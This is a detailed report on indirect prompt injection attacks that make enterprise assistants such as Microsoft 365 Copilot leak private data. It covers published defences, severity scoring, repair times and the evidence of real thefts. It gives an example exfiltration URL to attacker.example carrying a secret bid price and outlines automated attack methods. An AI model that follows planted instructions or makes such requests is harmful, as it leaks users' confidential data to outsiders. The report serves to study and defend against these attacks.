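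Choosing the score is difficult because injections are rare. Suppose a company receives a million emails a month, ten of them with injections, and its filter catches 95% of the injections and wrongly flags one ordinary email in a thousand. The filter will stop nine or ten attacks and about 1,000 harmless messages. Ordinary emails far outnumber injections at any company, so developers have to set the score high enough to avoid flagging too many of them, which lets more attacks through.

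EchoLeak passed Microsoft's XPIA classifier because Aim addressed the instructions to the human recipient. A customer and an attacker might send the same request for the latest price. The request is an attack when a model with access to private files will read it and the sender has no right to those files, but a classifier that examines only the text can't determine either condition.

Microsoft's researchers have therefore tried examining the model instead. Their TaskTracker compares the model's internal activity before and after it reads the outside text, and raises an alarm if the model seems to have started a new task. Even a politely worded email might trigger the alarm, because it has to change what the model is doing to cause a leak. Microsoft lists TaskTracker among its research projects and does not say that Copilot uses it.

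In July 2026 Microsoft added a filter that acts before an email reaches the mailbox. Microsoft (2026) announced that Defender for Office 365, its email security service, would detect injections aimed at AI assistants, and turned the feature on by default for customers with the Plan 2 or Microsoft 365 E5 subscription. According to Office 365 IT Pros' *Microsoft Defender for Office 365 Blocks Prompt Injections* (2026), Defender treats such a message as high-confidence phishing and quarantines it. In early August the feature was still in public preview.

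When Defender's email filter blocks a hostile email before delivery, no assistant that reads the mailbox can retrieve it. If the filter blocks a legitimate email by mistake, the employee cannot read it either. The filter also does not cover a hostile file that an employee downloads from a website and uploads to the assistant. The XPIA classifier, which failed against ReLeak, is a separate filter inside Copilot, so its failure is not evidence of how well Defender's filter works.

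### Marking untrusted text

A developer can also let the outside text through but mark it so the model can identify its source. *Defending Against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks With Spotlighting* (Hines et al., 2024) describes three ways to do this, all developed at Microsoft. In each, the standing instructions tell the model not to obey anything in the marked text.

- **Delimiting** puts a marker before and after the text. The software picks a random marker each time, so an attacker cannot write a fake end marker into an email.
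- **Datamarking** puts a special character between all the words, so a line of the stranger's email might read `add^the^price^to^the^link`.
- **Encoding** converts the whole text into a format such as Base64, which the model has to decode before it can summarise it.

Spotlighting reduced the success rate of attacks on the GPT models of the time from more than 50% to less than 2%, with little effect on the tasks the researchers tested. Encoding gave the strongest protection, but weaker models made mistakes decoding the text, so Hines and colleagues recommended it only for the most capable models. Developers can add spotlighting without retraining the model.

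Google tried a version of this on Gemini. *Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) describes software that inserted a special token every eight characters into an email's sender, subject and body. The researchers found that this worked mainly by breaking up the phrases that trigger an injection, so the model no longer received them as the usual tokens. They expected it to work less well in some languages.

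This explanation is less reassuring than the one behind spotlighting. If the marks mostly garble the attack, the model has not learned to treat text differently depending on its source, and an attacker can look for wording that survives the garbling. Ye and colleagues' probes also suggest this, since they responded more to a passage's style than to its label.

### Training the model to resist

Developers can also train a model to ignore injections. This training requires many convincing attacks, which they generate with other software. Google describes several automated attackers. One starts with a plain request for the user's private data and tries adding random tokens to the end, keeping those that make the assistant more likely to comply. This requires access to the model's probabilities, which an outsider normally lacks. A second attacker, called Tree of Attacks with Pruning (TAP), needs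 only the assistant's replies. It writes many versions of an attack in ordinary language, discards the weak ones and develops the rest.

Google DeepMind (2025) then trained Gemini on examples in which an automated attacker had planted instructions meant to extract sensitive information. The correct response was to ignore those instructions and do what the user had asked. According to SecurityWeek, the TAP attack's success rate in an email scenario fell from 99.8% against Gemini 2.0 to 53.6% against Gemini 2.5.

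OpenAI went further and trained a model to act as an automated attacker. *GPT-Red* (2026) describes training it through self-play, in which the attacker and defender improve against each other. The defender also has to keep completing legitimate tasks, because a model that refused to act on any email would be safe but useless to Dana.

The results that OpenAI and Anthropic published in 2026 are much better than Gemini's in 2025, but the companies ran different tests. The figures below are attack success rates.

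| Models compared | Test | Older model | Newer model |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.0 and 2.5 | TAP attack in an email scenario | 99.8% | 53.6% |
| GPT-6 Astra and its predecessor | OpenAI's automated attacker, average per query | 3.77% | 0.21% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol and GPT-6 Astra | Gray Swan benchmark, at least one success in 15 attempts | 27.0% | 8.5% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 and Opus 5 | Gray Swan benchmark, at least one success in 15 attempts | 5.5% | 2.0% |

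The figures for Astra come from OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026), which gives the first pair as defence rates of 96.23% and 99.79%. The figures for the Claude models come from Anthropic, as reported by The Decoder, a technology news site.

In OpenAI's internal test, the attacker's success rate was about 18 times lower against Astra than against the older model. An attacker would have needed about 18 tries for an even chance of success against the older model and would need about 330 against Astra. These estimates assume that attempts are independent, but in practice an email that fails against one employee's assistant will probably fail against a colleague's too, and one that an attacker has already tested successfully will probably work on many people. OpenAI also used the same family of attackers to train Astra, so the test may overstate its resistance.

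Gray Swan's benchmark is a useful check because the attacks came from outside. The security company selected 1,810 attacks from public contests held in early 2026. They cover coding, tool use and computer control, and their aims include data theft, data destruction and unauthorised payments. A rate of 8.5% therefore does not mean that 8.5% of hostile emails would extract a secret from an office assistant. Opus 5's result is lower than Astra's, but the two companies may have used different selections of attacks or safeguards, so the figures can't be used to rank the models.

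The Decoder also reports that no attack succeeded against Opus 5 as a browser agent in 129 test scenarios. If those were a random sample of the scenarios an agent might meet, attacks could succeed in up to about 2.3% of all such scenarios, at the 95% confidence level. Real attackers might also use kinds of attack that weren't in the test, which is a larger source of uncertainty.

Training protects the model in any product that uses it, and the user does not have to do anything. However, the tests measured a model with particular safeguards, and they do not show how it would behave in an enterprise assistant, which adds its own retrieval, instructions and tools. The ReLeak attacks do not show how Copilot would behave with the newest models either, since Cato sent Microsoft its last report on 20 August 2026, two weeks before OpenAI released Astra. OpenAI and Anthropic have since introduced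 newer models, described in *GPT-6.2 System Card* (2026) and *Introducing Claude Fable 5.2 and Claude Mythos 5.2* (2026).

### Attackers who can try again

Testing a defence against a fixed set of attacks shows how it handles attacks its developers already know about. But an attacker with an account on the same product can read the product's replies, reword the attack and try again, as Radware did with Deep Research and Cato's agents did with Copilot.

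*LLMail-Inject* (Abdelnabi, Fay and colleagues, 2025) describes a contest of the same name in which Microsoft invited the public to attack a simulated email assistant. The assistant's user asked ordinary questions about a mailbox, and contestants could only send the assistant emails. To win a level, they had to make it send an email that the user had not asked for, with the right content and to the right address. On some levels, retrieval also had to select the hostile email from among others. The organisers varied the model and the defence, which could be spotlighting, Prompt Shields, TaskTracker, a second language model acting as judge, or all four together.

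The contest's 839 participants submitted 208,095 different attacks. Microsoft's figure of more than 370,000 prompts includes repeats. Most attempts failed, but some contestants succeeded. The low success rate per attempt offers little reassurance, because contestants learned from their failures and needed only one email that worked. The models were small by today's standards, so the results are more useful for studying how people adapt than for judging current products. Microsoft published the whole collection, which gives developers more of the training examples that Ravia had found to be scarce.

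Gray Swan's contest used stronger models. Dziemian (2026) reports that 464 people made more than 272,000 attempts against 13 leading models. They had to make an agent do something harmful without revealing the attack in its final answer. EchoLeak was hidden in a similar way, since the employee received a normal answer that did not cite the hostile email. Each model failed to resist at least one attack.

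The most damaging evidence against published defences is *The Attacker Moves Second*, an October 2025 paper by Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, a group that included researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind. It tested 12 defences against prompt injection and jailbreaks (attempts by the user to make a model break its rules). Most of the defences' developers had reported that almost no attacks succeeded. The group designed attacks for each defence, using automated search and human contestants, and got past most of the defences more than 90% of the time. The defences that failed included spotlighting, several classifiers and several specially trained models.

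These attackers had more time and computing power than someone who sends a few emails, and some could use information about the model that Copilot customers do not have, so their success rates are close to a worst case. But the developers' near-zero figures came from tests with attackers who never adjusted to the defence. A company deciding how much private data to give an assistant should give little weight to a low success rate unless the testers were free to adapt their attacks to the defence.

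### Labels that follow the data

These weaknesses would matter little if the assistant could not send the price to the stranger even after obeying the email. Information-flow control tries to guarantee this by labeling data and checking the labels before the assistant acts. The method is older than language models. An ordinary program checks the labels, and it does not follow instructions in planted text.

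Suppose Dana's assistant can open web addresses and send email. Dana's colleague Ilse is also working on the bid. Each piece of text has one label showing whether an outsider could have influenced it and another listing who may read it.

| Text | Could an outsider have influenced it? | Who may read it |
|---|---|---|
| The internal note with the price | No | Dana, Ilse and the rest of the bid team |
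| The stranger's email | Yes | Dana and the stranger |
| Whatever the model writes after reading both | Yes | Dana |

The last row follows from two rules. A mixture is untrusted if any part of it is, and only people who may read every part may read the whole:

readers(mixture) = readers(note) ∩ readers(email)

where ∩ means the people who are on both lists.

Suppose the email's instructions work and the model generates a request to open `https://attacker.example/p?bid=4200000`. The program checks the request against its rules and blocks it for two separate reasons. An outsider could have influenced the decision to open the address, and the stranger isn't allowed to read anything based on the note.

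The program checks labels, so it does not need to recognise the price. Converting the price to Base64 would make no difference. Neither would using a set of prepared addresses, one for each digit, like those that got past OpenAI's url_safe check, because the model's choice of address has the same labels as everything the model has read. In Dana's original case the price left through an image, so the chat window would have to submit images to the same check before loading them.

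This simple version would be annoying to use. Once the stranger's email is in the context, it restricts everything the assistant does for the rest of the conversation. Dana can no longer have the assistant send Ilse the list of tasks, even though Ilse is allowed to read the note.

Costa and colleagues at Microsoft describe a remedy, called FIDES, in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (2025). If adding a search result to the context would tighten the context's labels, FIDES puts the result in a variable (a named container) and tells the planning model only the name. Dana's request would then go like this:

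1. Dana asks the assistant to send Ilse the remaining tasks from the internal note.
2. The search finds the note and the stranger's email, and FIDES stores them as `note_1` and `mail_1`.
3. The planning model asks a second model, which has no tools, to extract the tasks from `note_1`. FIDES stores the answer as `tasks_1`, with the note's labels.
4. The planning model asks to send `tasks_1` to Ilse. The program finds that Ilse may read it, and sends it.

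The planning model never reads the stranger's instructions, so they cannot change the plan. If the plan depends on something in the email, such as whether the sender mentions a deadline, the planning model can have the second model read `mail_1` with its output restricted to yes or no. The stranger could still make that answer wrong, but could not use it to pass along a new instruction.

*Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues, 2025) describes CaMeL, a design from Google DeepMind and ETH Zurich that uses a similar division. One model turns the user's request into a short program before the system reads any outside text. A second model, without tools, reads emails and documents when the program needs information from them. An interpreter runs the program, tracks where each value came from and who may read it, and checks these records at every tool call.

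In tests on AgentDojo, a set of simulated office, banking, travel and messaging tasks, an assistant with CaMeL's guarantees completed 77% of the tasks, compared with 84% for one without those guarantees. The assistant with CaMeL also used nearly three times as many tokens, which makes each answer slower and more expensive.

Some of the lost tasks are hard to recover because the user wants the assistant to follow instructions in an email. If Dana writes "do what the customer asks in this email", nobody can write the plan without reading the email. The assistant would have to ask Dana to approve each step.

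*Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) compares the design with an ordinary sandbox. If a sandbox allows the assistant to send email, a planted instruction can still make it send private data in a plausible-looking message. CaMeL would also check where the contents of that message came from. The paper identifies a weakness in CaMeL's use of a restricted form of Python. An error can make a Python program stop or take a different path, which makes it hard to prove that no information escapes. For instance, if a program stops whenever Dana's price is above four million, an outsider can learn something about the price by noticing that an expected message never came. The paper therefore recommends a simpler language designed for security.

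The labels also have to be correct. If Dana downloads a guide containing an attacker's text and saves it in the bid team's folder, software that trusts everything in that folder will trust the attacker's text. Neither design stops a hostile email from making its own summary false, because Dana is allowed to read that summary.

Another advantage of information-flow control over filters is that it does not depend on an attacker being present. OpenAI tested its models on difficult workplace tasks with ambiguous instructions and complicated permissions. Astra sent data where it should not have in 4.3% of runs, or 4.5% when OpenAI gave it a policy on when to ask for the user's approval. The older GPT-5.6 Sol did so in 14.1% of runs without the policy and 8.8% with it. A check on who may read the data could stop these mistakes in the same way as theft.

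### Limiting what the assistant can read

Administrators cannot redesign Copilot, but they can restrict what it retrieves. Excluding email from outside the company would have stopped EchoLeak and ReLeak, however the attackers had worded their emails. But this restriction may make the assistant much less useful to someone in sales or purchasing.

The setting also leaves gaps. An outsider's email would arrive as internal mail if an employee forwarded it to a colleague, unless the software tracked its origin. An attacker who had taken over a supplier's account could exploit any exception for trusted senders. Attacks can also come through shared documents and web pages, as those on Gemini Enterprise and ChatGPT showed.

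Sensitivity labels protect the private data instead. Microsoft says its Purview software can prevent Copilot from summarising labelled files covered by a data loss prevention policy. If Dana's firm had such a rule for bids, the note would stay out of the context.

Dana would then get no help with her tasks, because they are in the same note as the price. Labels work best for a small amount of very sensitive material that employees rarely need the assistant to read, such as merger plans. They are less practical for documents that people use all day.

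Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) proposes a broader rule for AI agents. Within one session, an agent should have no more than two of these three properties: it processes untrusted input, it has access to private data or sensitive systems, and it can change something or communicate externally. If a task requires all three, a person has to supervise the agent, for instance by approving its actions, unless some other reliable check can do so.

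The list is close to Willison's lethal trifecta, but Meta's third property includes actions such as deleting a file or paying a bill, which can do damage without leaking anything. Dana's assistant already reads outside email and private files, so under Meta's rule it should not load an image from an outside server or send a message on its own. It could draft a reply to a customer for Dana to read and send.

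Willison welcomed the rule but objected that Meta's diagram marked every pair of properties as safe. An agent that reads hostile text and can change things may cause harm even without access to private data. Meta replaced "safe" with "lower risk". The rule also works only if the person applying it knows what the agent can do. An administrator who read Microsoft's documentation in the summer of 2026 would have believed that Copilot's code interpreter could not communicate externally, but Rubrik and Cato showed that it could.

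### What Microsoft 365 Copilot uses

In July 2025, the month after EchoLeak became public, Microsoft's security team described its layered defences. The team hardens the standing instructions and marks untrusted text, uses classifiers to detect injections, and designs its products so that an injection that gets through should do no harm. Microsoft also advises developers to assume that indirect prompt injection is inevitable and to design systems that contain it.

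The July account covers techniques that Microsoft uses internally, offers to customers or is still researching, usually without specifying which of them protect Copilot. The following description is based on that account and outside researchers' findings.

| Measure | Evidence about Microsoft 365 Copilot |
|---|---|
| Injection classifier | Copilot uses one. Aim got past it in 2025 and Cato in 2026 |
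| Spotlighting | Microsoft says it uses the technique internally, without naming Copilot |
| Blocking images and untrusted links | Microsoft says it blocks known techniques, and researchers met these filters in Copilot |
| Sensitivity labels and data loss prevention rules | Microsoft names Copilot, but customers have to set them up |
| Approval by the user | Microsoft names Copilot in Outlook, which drafts an email that the user then has to send |
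| Injection filter in Defender | Protects the mailbox that Copilot reads, for customers with certain subscriptions |
| TaskTracker and FIDES | Microsoft describes both as research |

Prompt Shields is missing from the table because Microsoft does not say whether it is the classifier that researchers encountered in Copilot. In a later post about attempts to manipulate assistants' memories, Microsoft wrote that it continues to deploy protections against prompt injection in Copilot, but that statement does not identify them.

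After EchoLeak, Reddy and Gujral recommended isolating text by its source, using better filters, and controlling the model's output more tightly. FIDES would guarantee that isolation, and in July 2025 Microsoft said this line of research would be the basis for its next generation of defences. A year later, the ReLeak emails could still direct Copilot. If Copilot had by then checked where data came from and who was allowed to read it before every outgoing request, the image request that went through Bing should have failed, because the image's address contained data the attacker had no right to read.

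## Severity scores, repair times and evidence of real attacks

Microsoft gave EchoLeak a severity score of 9.3 out of 10, and the US government's National Vulnerability Database (NVD) gave it 7.5. Both used version 3.1 of CVSS, a formula that calculates severity from the answers to eight questions about a flaw, but they answered two of the questions differently.

### How EchoLeak got two scores

The record at GCVE contains both sets of answers. CVSS calls such a set a vector and abbreviates each answer, as shown in brackets:

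| Question | Microsoft | NVD |
|---|---|---|
| How the attacker reaches the system | Over a network (AV:N) | Over a network (AV:N) |
| Difficulty of the attack | Low (AC:L) | Low (AC:L) |
| Account the attacker needs | None (PR:N) | None (PR:N) |
| Action needed from a user | None (UI:N) | None (UI:N) |
| Scope | Changed (S:C) | Unchanged (S:U) |
| Loss of confidentiality | High (C:H) | High (C:H) |
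| Loss of integrity | Low (I:L) | None (I:N) |
| Loss of availability | None (A:N) | None (A:N) |

The scorers agreed on the first four answers, which describe how hard the attack is, but disagreed on scope and integrity. Scope is "changed" if a flaw in one component lets an attacker harm something a different component is supposed to protect. Integrity measures whether the attacker can alter data.

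The formula adds a number for how easy the attack is to a number for its impact. The first is the same for both scorers:

8.22 × 0.85 × 0.77 × 0.85 × 0.85 ≈ 3.89

For the impact, a high loss counts as 0.56, a low one as 0.22 and none as 0, and the formula combines them as 1 − (1 − C)(1 − I)(1 − A). NVD's answers give 0.56. With unchanged scope the formula multiplies this by 6.42, which gives 3.60, and the total of 7.48 rounds up to 7.5. Microsoft's answers give 1 − 0.44 × 0.78, or about 0.66. Changed scope brings in a steeper scale, which turns this into 4.72, and then raises the total by 8%, to 9.3 after rounding up. Changing one answer at a time shows how much each contributes:

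| Scope | Integrity loss | Score |
|---|---|---|
| Unchanged | None | 7.5 (NVD) |
| Unchanged | Low | 8.2 |
| Changed | None | 8.6 |
| Changed | Low | 9.3 (Microsoft) |

Neither Microsoft nor NVD explained its choices. Microsoft describes the flaw only as a disclosure of information, which supports NVD's integrity rating. Microsoft may have counted the planted text's changes to Copilot's answer as a loss of integrity. Scope is harder to judge because Copilot, the mailbox and the Teams server that forwarded the data all belong to Microsoft, and it is unclear whether they count as one system.

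Both scorers said the attack required no user interaction, which is also open to question because the victim had to ask Copilot something. If that counted as interaction, Microsoft's 9.3 would fall to 8.2. CVSS 4.0, published in 2023, has an intermediate value called "passive" for a user who triggers an attack through ordinary use. That value seems to fit EchoLeak better than either option in version 3.1.

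### SearchLeak and the click

SearchLeak, the 2026 attack by Varonis, began when the victim clicked a link, so Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026) lists user interaction as required (UI:R) and gives a score of 6.5. *CVE-2026-42824* (2026), a page on a vulnerability tracking site, shows that NVD received Microsoft's vector on 4 June and added its own on 8 June. NVD's vector differs only in that it lists user interaction as not required, which raises the score to 7.5.

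Microsoft's vector is better than NVD's because the attacker's prompt did not run until somebody clicked a link. NVD's analysts may not have known that, because they scored the flaw a week before Varonis described the attack. The public description at the time was a single sentence that did not mention a link, although Microsoft's vector did record the user interaction. Published vectors for another Copilot flaw that May also differed on user interaction. Exploit Intel's *CVE-2026-42827* (2026) lists a vector with it and a score of 6.5, while Secualive's *CVE-2026-42827* (2026) lists one without it and a score of 7.5.

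News reports added to the confusion. The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox* states that NVD also gave SearchLeak 6.5, but the change history contradicts this. Expert Insights' *Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Let One Click Exfiltrate Emails* (2026) gives both scores correctly but attributes the "critical" rating to Varonis. Varonis did use the word, but Microsoft's record also lists "Critical" next to the 6.5.

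Microsoft assigns severity labels on its own scale, separately from CVSS, so a flaw's label and CVSS score can differ widely. For example, STAR Labs' *CVE-2026-24299* (2026) lists a "Critical" label and a CVSS score of 5.3 for the Copilot flaws that Rehberger reported in 2025. The score is lower partly because the attack is rated as difficult to carry out (AC:H).

Even scores from the same company are hard to compare. Microsoft scored EchoLeak 2.8 points higher than SearchLeak. Only SearchLeak requires a click, which explains 1.1 points of the difference. The other 1.7 arise because Microsoft recorded a changed scope and some loss of integrity for EchoLeak and neither for SearchLeak, although both attacks sent private data out through another Microsoft service.

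A similar judgement may explain why the score for ReLeak's code interpreter attack rose from 7.4 to 8.6. Under the formula, a flaw with changed scope and a high loss of confidentiality alone scores 7.4 if it requires user interaction and 8.6 if it does not. Other combinations also produce 7.4, so this is a guess. If it is right, someone first counted the victim's question to Copilot as user interaction and later did not.

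### What a CVE means when there is nothing to install

A CVE record normally lists the versions of a program that administrators need to replace. Customers cannot choose a version of Copilot, and the EchoLeak record has a dash in place of a version number, along with the tag "exclusively hosted service". Microsoft said it issued the EchoLeak CVE "to provide further transparency", and it gives the same reason in the SearchLeak record.

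The entry still gives the flaw a common name, a type and a publication date, but it omits the date the flaw first appeared. A company checking its old records for signs of an attack therefore knows roughly when the danger ended but not how far back to look.

Since 2024, Microsoft has issued CVEs for cloud flaws that it rates critical. Many of the other cases appear to have no CVE, including the image leaks in ChatGPT and Bard, the attack on Slack AI and Rehberger's 2024 attack on Copilot. MITRE refused Schwartzman a CVE because customers do not control ChatGPT. The same is true of Copilot, so the difference is due to the vendor's policy. Comparing assistants by CVE count would make Microsoft look worse partly because it publishes more CVEs.

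Automated services also handle these entries badly. The Exploit Prediction Scoring System (EPSS) estimates the probability that someone will observe attempts to exploit a flaw in the next 30 days. On 16 November 2026, its figure for EchoLeak was 7.2%, higher than for about 94% of all CVEs. Microsoft had closed the flaw for every customer 18 months earlier, so the figure does not indicate the risk to a company that uses Copilot today.

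### How long the repairs took

Repair times in the table run from the finder's report to the vendor's fix. "By" marks the date when the finder learned of or noticed the fix, so the vendor may have fixed the flaw earlier.

| Attack | Reported | Fixed | Time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Bing Chat, image leak | 8 April 2023 | By 15 June 2023 | At most 68 days |
| ChatGPT, image leak | 9 April 2023 | December 2023, partly | About 8 months |
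| Bard, image leak | 19 September 2023 | By 19 October 2023 | At most 30 days |
| Microsoft 365 Copilot, invisible text in a link | 10 February 2024 | By 2 July 2024 | At most 143 days |
| Slack AI | 14 August 2024 | 20 August 2024 | 6 days |
| EchoLeak | January 2025 | May 2025 | About 4 months |
| ForcedLeak | 28 July 2025 | 8 September 2025 | 42 days |
| Reprompt | 31 August 2025 | 13 January 2026 | 135 days |
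| CoSnitch | December 2025 | 18 August 2026 | About 8 months |
| ReLeak, code interpreter | 29 July to 20 August 2026 | 17 September 2026 | 28 to 50 days |
| ReLeak, saved files | 29 July to 20 August 2026 | 11 November 2026 | 83 to 105 days |
| ReLeak, Bing image | 29 July to 20 August 2026 | 15 November 2026 | 87 to 109 days |

The ReLeak rows have ranges because Cato gave one reporting period for all three attacks.

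These numbers are a poor basis for ranking the vendors. Removing an image from a chat page is a smaller job than repairing a sandbox, and a vendor that takes longer may be fixing more. EchoLeak, for instance, needed more work after Microsoft's first attempt to fix it. *Microsoft patches a Copilot flaw that let one click steal your data* (Kantra, 2026) calls the August repair of CoSnitch the "final" fix, so Microsoft may have closed parts of that attack earlier.

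The starting dates are not equivalent either. In the table, the repair time for the 2024 attack on Copilot starts on the day Rehberger sent the whole attack, 24 days after he first reported the invisible characters. "Fixed" also covers everything from OpenAI's check on image addresses, which still let some data out, to GitHub's removal of all images from Copilot Chat. Because some repairs are only partial, the same kind of leak can return even after a fast one.

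Publicity may also affect repair times. Slack's was by far the shortest, at six days, and it released its patch on the day PromptArmor published the attack. Publication did not have the same effect on Atlassian. Rovo was still vulnerable to the attack through an uploaded file when PromptArmor published it, 74 days after reporting it, and the table gives no repair date because none has been confirmed.

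Finders also choose what to publish and usually wait for a fix, so the table is missing flaws that vendors are still working on and flaws that finders reported and then forgot about. The table also doesn't show how vendors treat researchers. Rehberger complained about slow answers from several companies, but he also recalls on Embrace The Red that Microsoft was the first vendor to acknowledge his report of the image leak in 2023.

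### Who said that no customers were affected

Windows Central's *Microsoft Copilot's own default configuration exposed users* quotes a Microsoft spokesman who thanked Aim for reporting EchoLeak so that Microsoft could address it "before our customers were impacted". Aim's co-founder Gruss said, more cautiously, that the evidence gathered suggested no customers had been affected. On 14 June 2025 the US cybersecurity agency CISA recorded EchoLeak's exploitation status as "none".

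Microsoft's record for SearchLeak lists exploitation as "No". According to The Next Web, the company said it had no evidence of malicious use, which is a weaker claim.

Antipov reports that Cato, which found ReLeak, had no information about affected customers or real attacks when it published. The line under the headline of Faisal's article attributes this statement to Microsoft, but the article itself attributes it to Cato. The difference matters because Cato can know about its own customers and tests but cannot search Microsoft's servers. Slack's 2024 statement was limited to the evidence the company had at the time.

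None of these statements included details of what anyone had searched. Microsoft is best placed to check, since its servers carried much of the traffic, but readers cannot tell from its one-word "No" whether it searched months of logs or simply received no complaints.

### What an investigator could find

Nexo Causal's *ReLeak* (2026), an article on a Brazilian forensics site, describes how a company might investigate such a leak. The company would collect the outside emails that arrived in the period, the assistant's answers that contain image addresses, the browser's requests to outside domains, and the record of what Copilot looked up in mailboxes and files. The investigator would then match the outside email to the employee's question and the outgoing request.

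This would work well in Dana's case, because her browser contacted attacker.example directly a moment after she asked about the harbour bid, and the address it requested contained the price.

A search of the company's own traffic for unfamiliar domains would find no trace of EchoLeak or ReLeak, because the request that reached the attacker came from Microsoft's servers. Only Microsoft could supply evidence of that request, the last step in the attack.

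The first piece may also be missing if the assistant did not cite the attacker's text, as in EchoLeak and Slack AI. Without a record of what Copilot retrieved, an investigator would have to guess which of thousands of emails contained the instructions.

In the Reprompt attack, the attacker's server sent its commands after the first prompt, so the link in the victim's browser history does not show what the attacker asked for, according to Cloud Security Alliance's *Reprompt*. Software on the victim's computer could not detect the theft.

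Even a company that discovers a theft may not connect it to the assistant. If an attacker used ForcedLeak to copy a list of sales leads, the company might learn of it when a competitor started calling those leads, and it might suspect an employee. If the attacker stole a password or login code, the resulting break-in would look ordinary.

The lack of public reports is therefore only weak evidence that no thefts have occurred. If, for illustration, each theft had a one-in-20 chance of becoming public, independently of the others, the chance of hearing about none of ten thefts would be 0.95¹⁰, or about 60%. For 100 thefts, it would be about 0.6%. On these assumptions, the lack of reports makes widespread theft unlikely but is compatible with a few successful attacks on chosen targets.

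### Attempts, demonstrations and thefts

*Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* proposes a scale for sorting such evidence:

- Level A is an attack that researchers built and measured under controlled conditions.
- Level B is insecure behaviour in a real, unmodified product, without proof of malicious intent.
- Level C is a confirmed incident outside the laboratory, such as the exposure of a user's information.
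- Level D is a claim without a reproducible observation.

The email worm that Cohen, Bitton and Nassi ran on their own assistant belongs at level A. EchoLeak, SearchLeak and ReLeak fit level B best because researchers demonstrated them on Microsoft's own service. No theft has been publicly confirmed for any of the attacks on enterprise assistants described here, so none is at level C.

Under the scale's rules, a second-hand report cannot raise the level of the event it describes. This matters for EchoLeak because some second-hand reports present it as a real attack. Intruder's *CVE-2025-32711*, a page that collects social media posts about the flaw, includes two from August 2026 that label it an "attack in the wild". Another post, from a security vendor's research team, describes attackers using indirect prompt injection to gain a first foothold and gives EchoLeak as an example. Fadilpašić's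 headline similarly overstates ReLeak by calling it a "campaign".

Tracking sites can mislead in a similar way. According to one site's page for CVE-2026-42824, a public exploit for SearchLeak is available on GitHub. The only project the page lists is a self-described archive of Chinese technology newsletters, which presumably mentioned the CVE number.

The evidence is better for attempts with other aims. In February 2026 Microsoft described companies that put hidden instructions behind "Summarize with AI" buttons on their websites. Clicking a button opened the visitor's assistant with a prompt already in the link, much as in Reprompt, and the prompt included an instruction to remember the company as a trusted source. The companies used this method on ordinary users as a form of advertising, and Microsoft's account is not evidence that anyone used it to take private data.

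The new injection filter in Defender for Office 365 suggests that Microsoft expects hostile instructions in customers' mail. Counting what the filter blocks would help show how common these attempts are, but not whether any data was stolen. Confirming a theft would require evidence that an assistant retrieved the instructions and followed them, and that the data reached an outsider.

### Finders who sell protection

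Many of the finders have a commercial interest in defending against such attacks. Aim had already developed a product against "LLM scope violations" when it introduced the term. Simonovich published ReLeak on a page with a menu of Cato's products for protecting employees' use of AI, AI applications and AI agents, and for testing AI systems by attacking them. Varonis, which published four of the 2026 attacks, is a data security company that sells help with controlling who can access which data. After SearchLeak, it sensibly advised tightening that control, among other measures, so that Copilot indexes less data.

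Readers may not notice the connection when the text appears elsewhere. The Cloud Security Alliance, a non-profit, republished Taler's account of SearchLeak on its site with a one-line credit to Varonis.

The commercial interest is little reason to doubt that the flaws existed. Vendors confirmed most of them and changed their products, and Atlassian paid Varonis for reporting one. Researchers such as Samoilenko, Schwartzman and Rehberger found the same kinds of leak without launching a security product at the same time.

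The finders' commercial interest is more likely to affect what they leave out. A company that sells protection has little reason to publish its failed attempts, and neither Aim nor Radware said how many attempts its tests involved. Words like "first" and "critical" also attract customers. The assistants' vendors have the opposite incentive, to describe a flaw as narrow, as Slack did in 2024.
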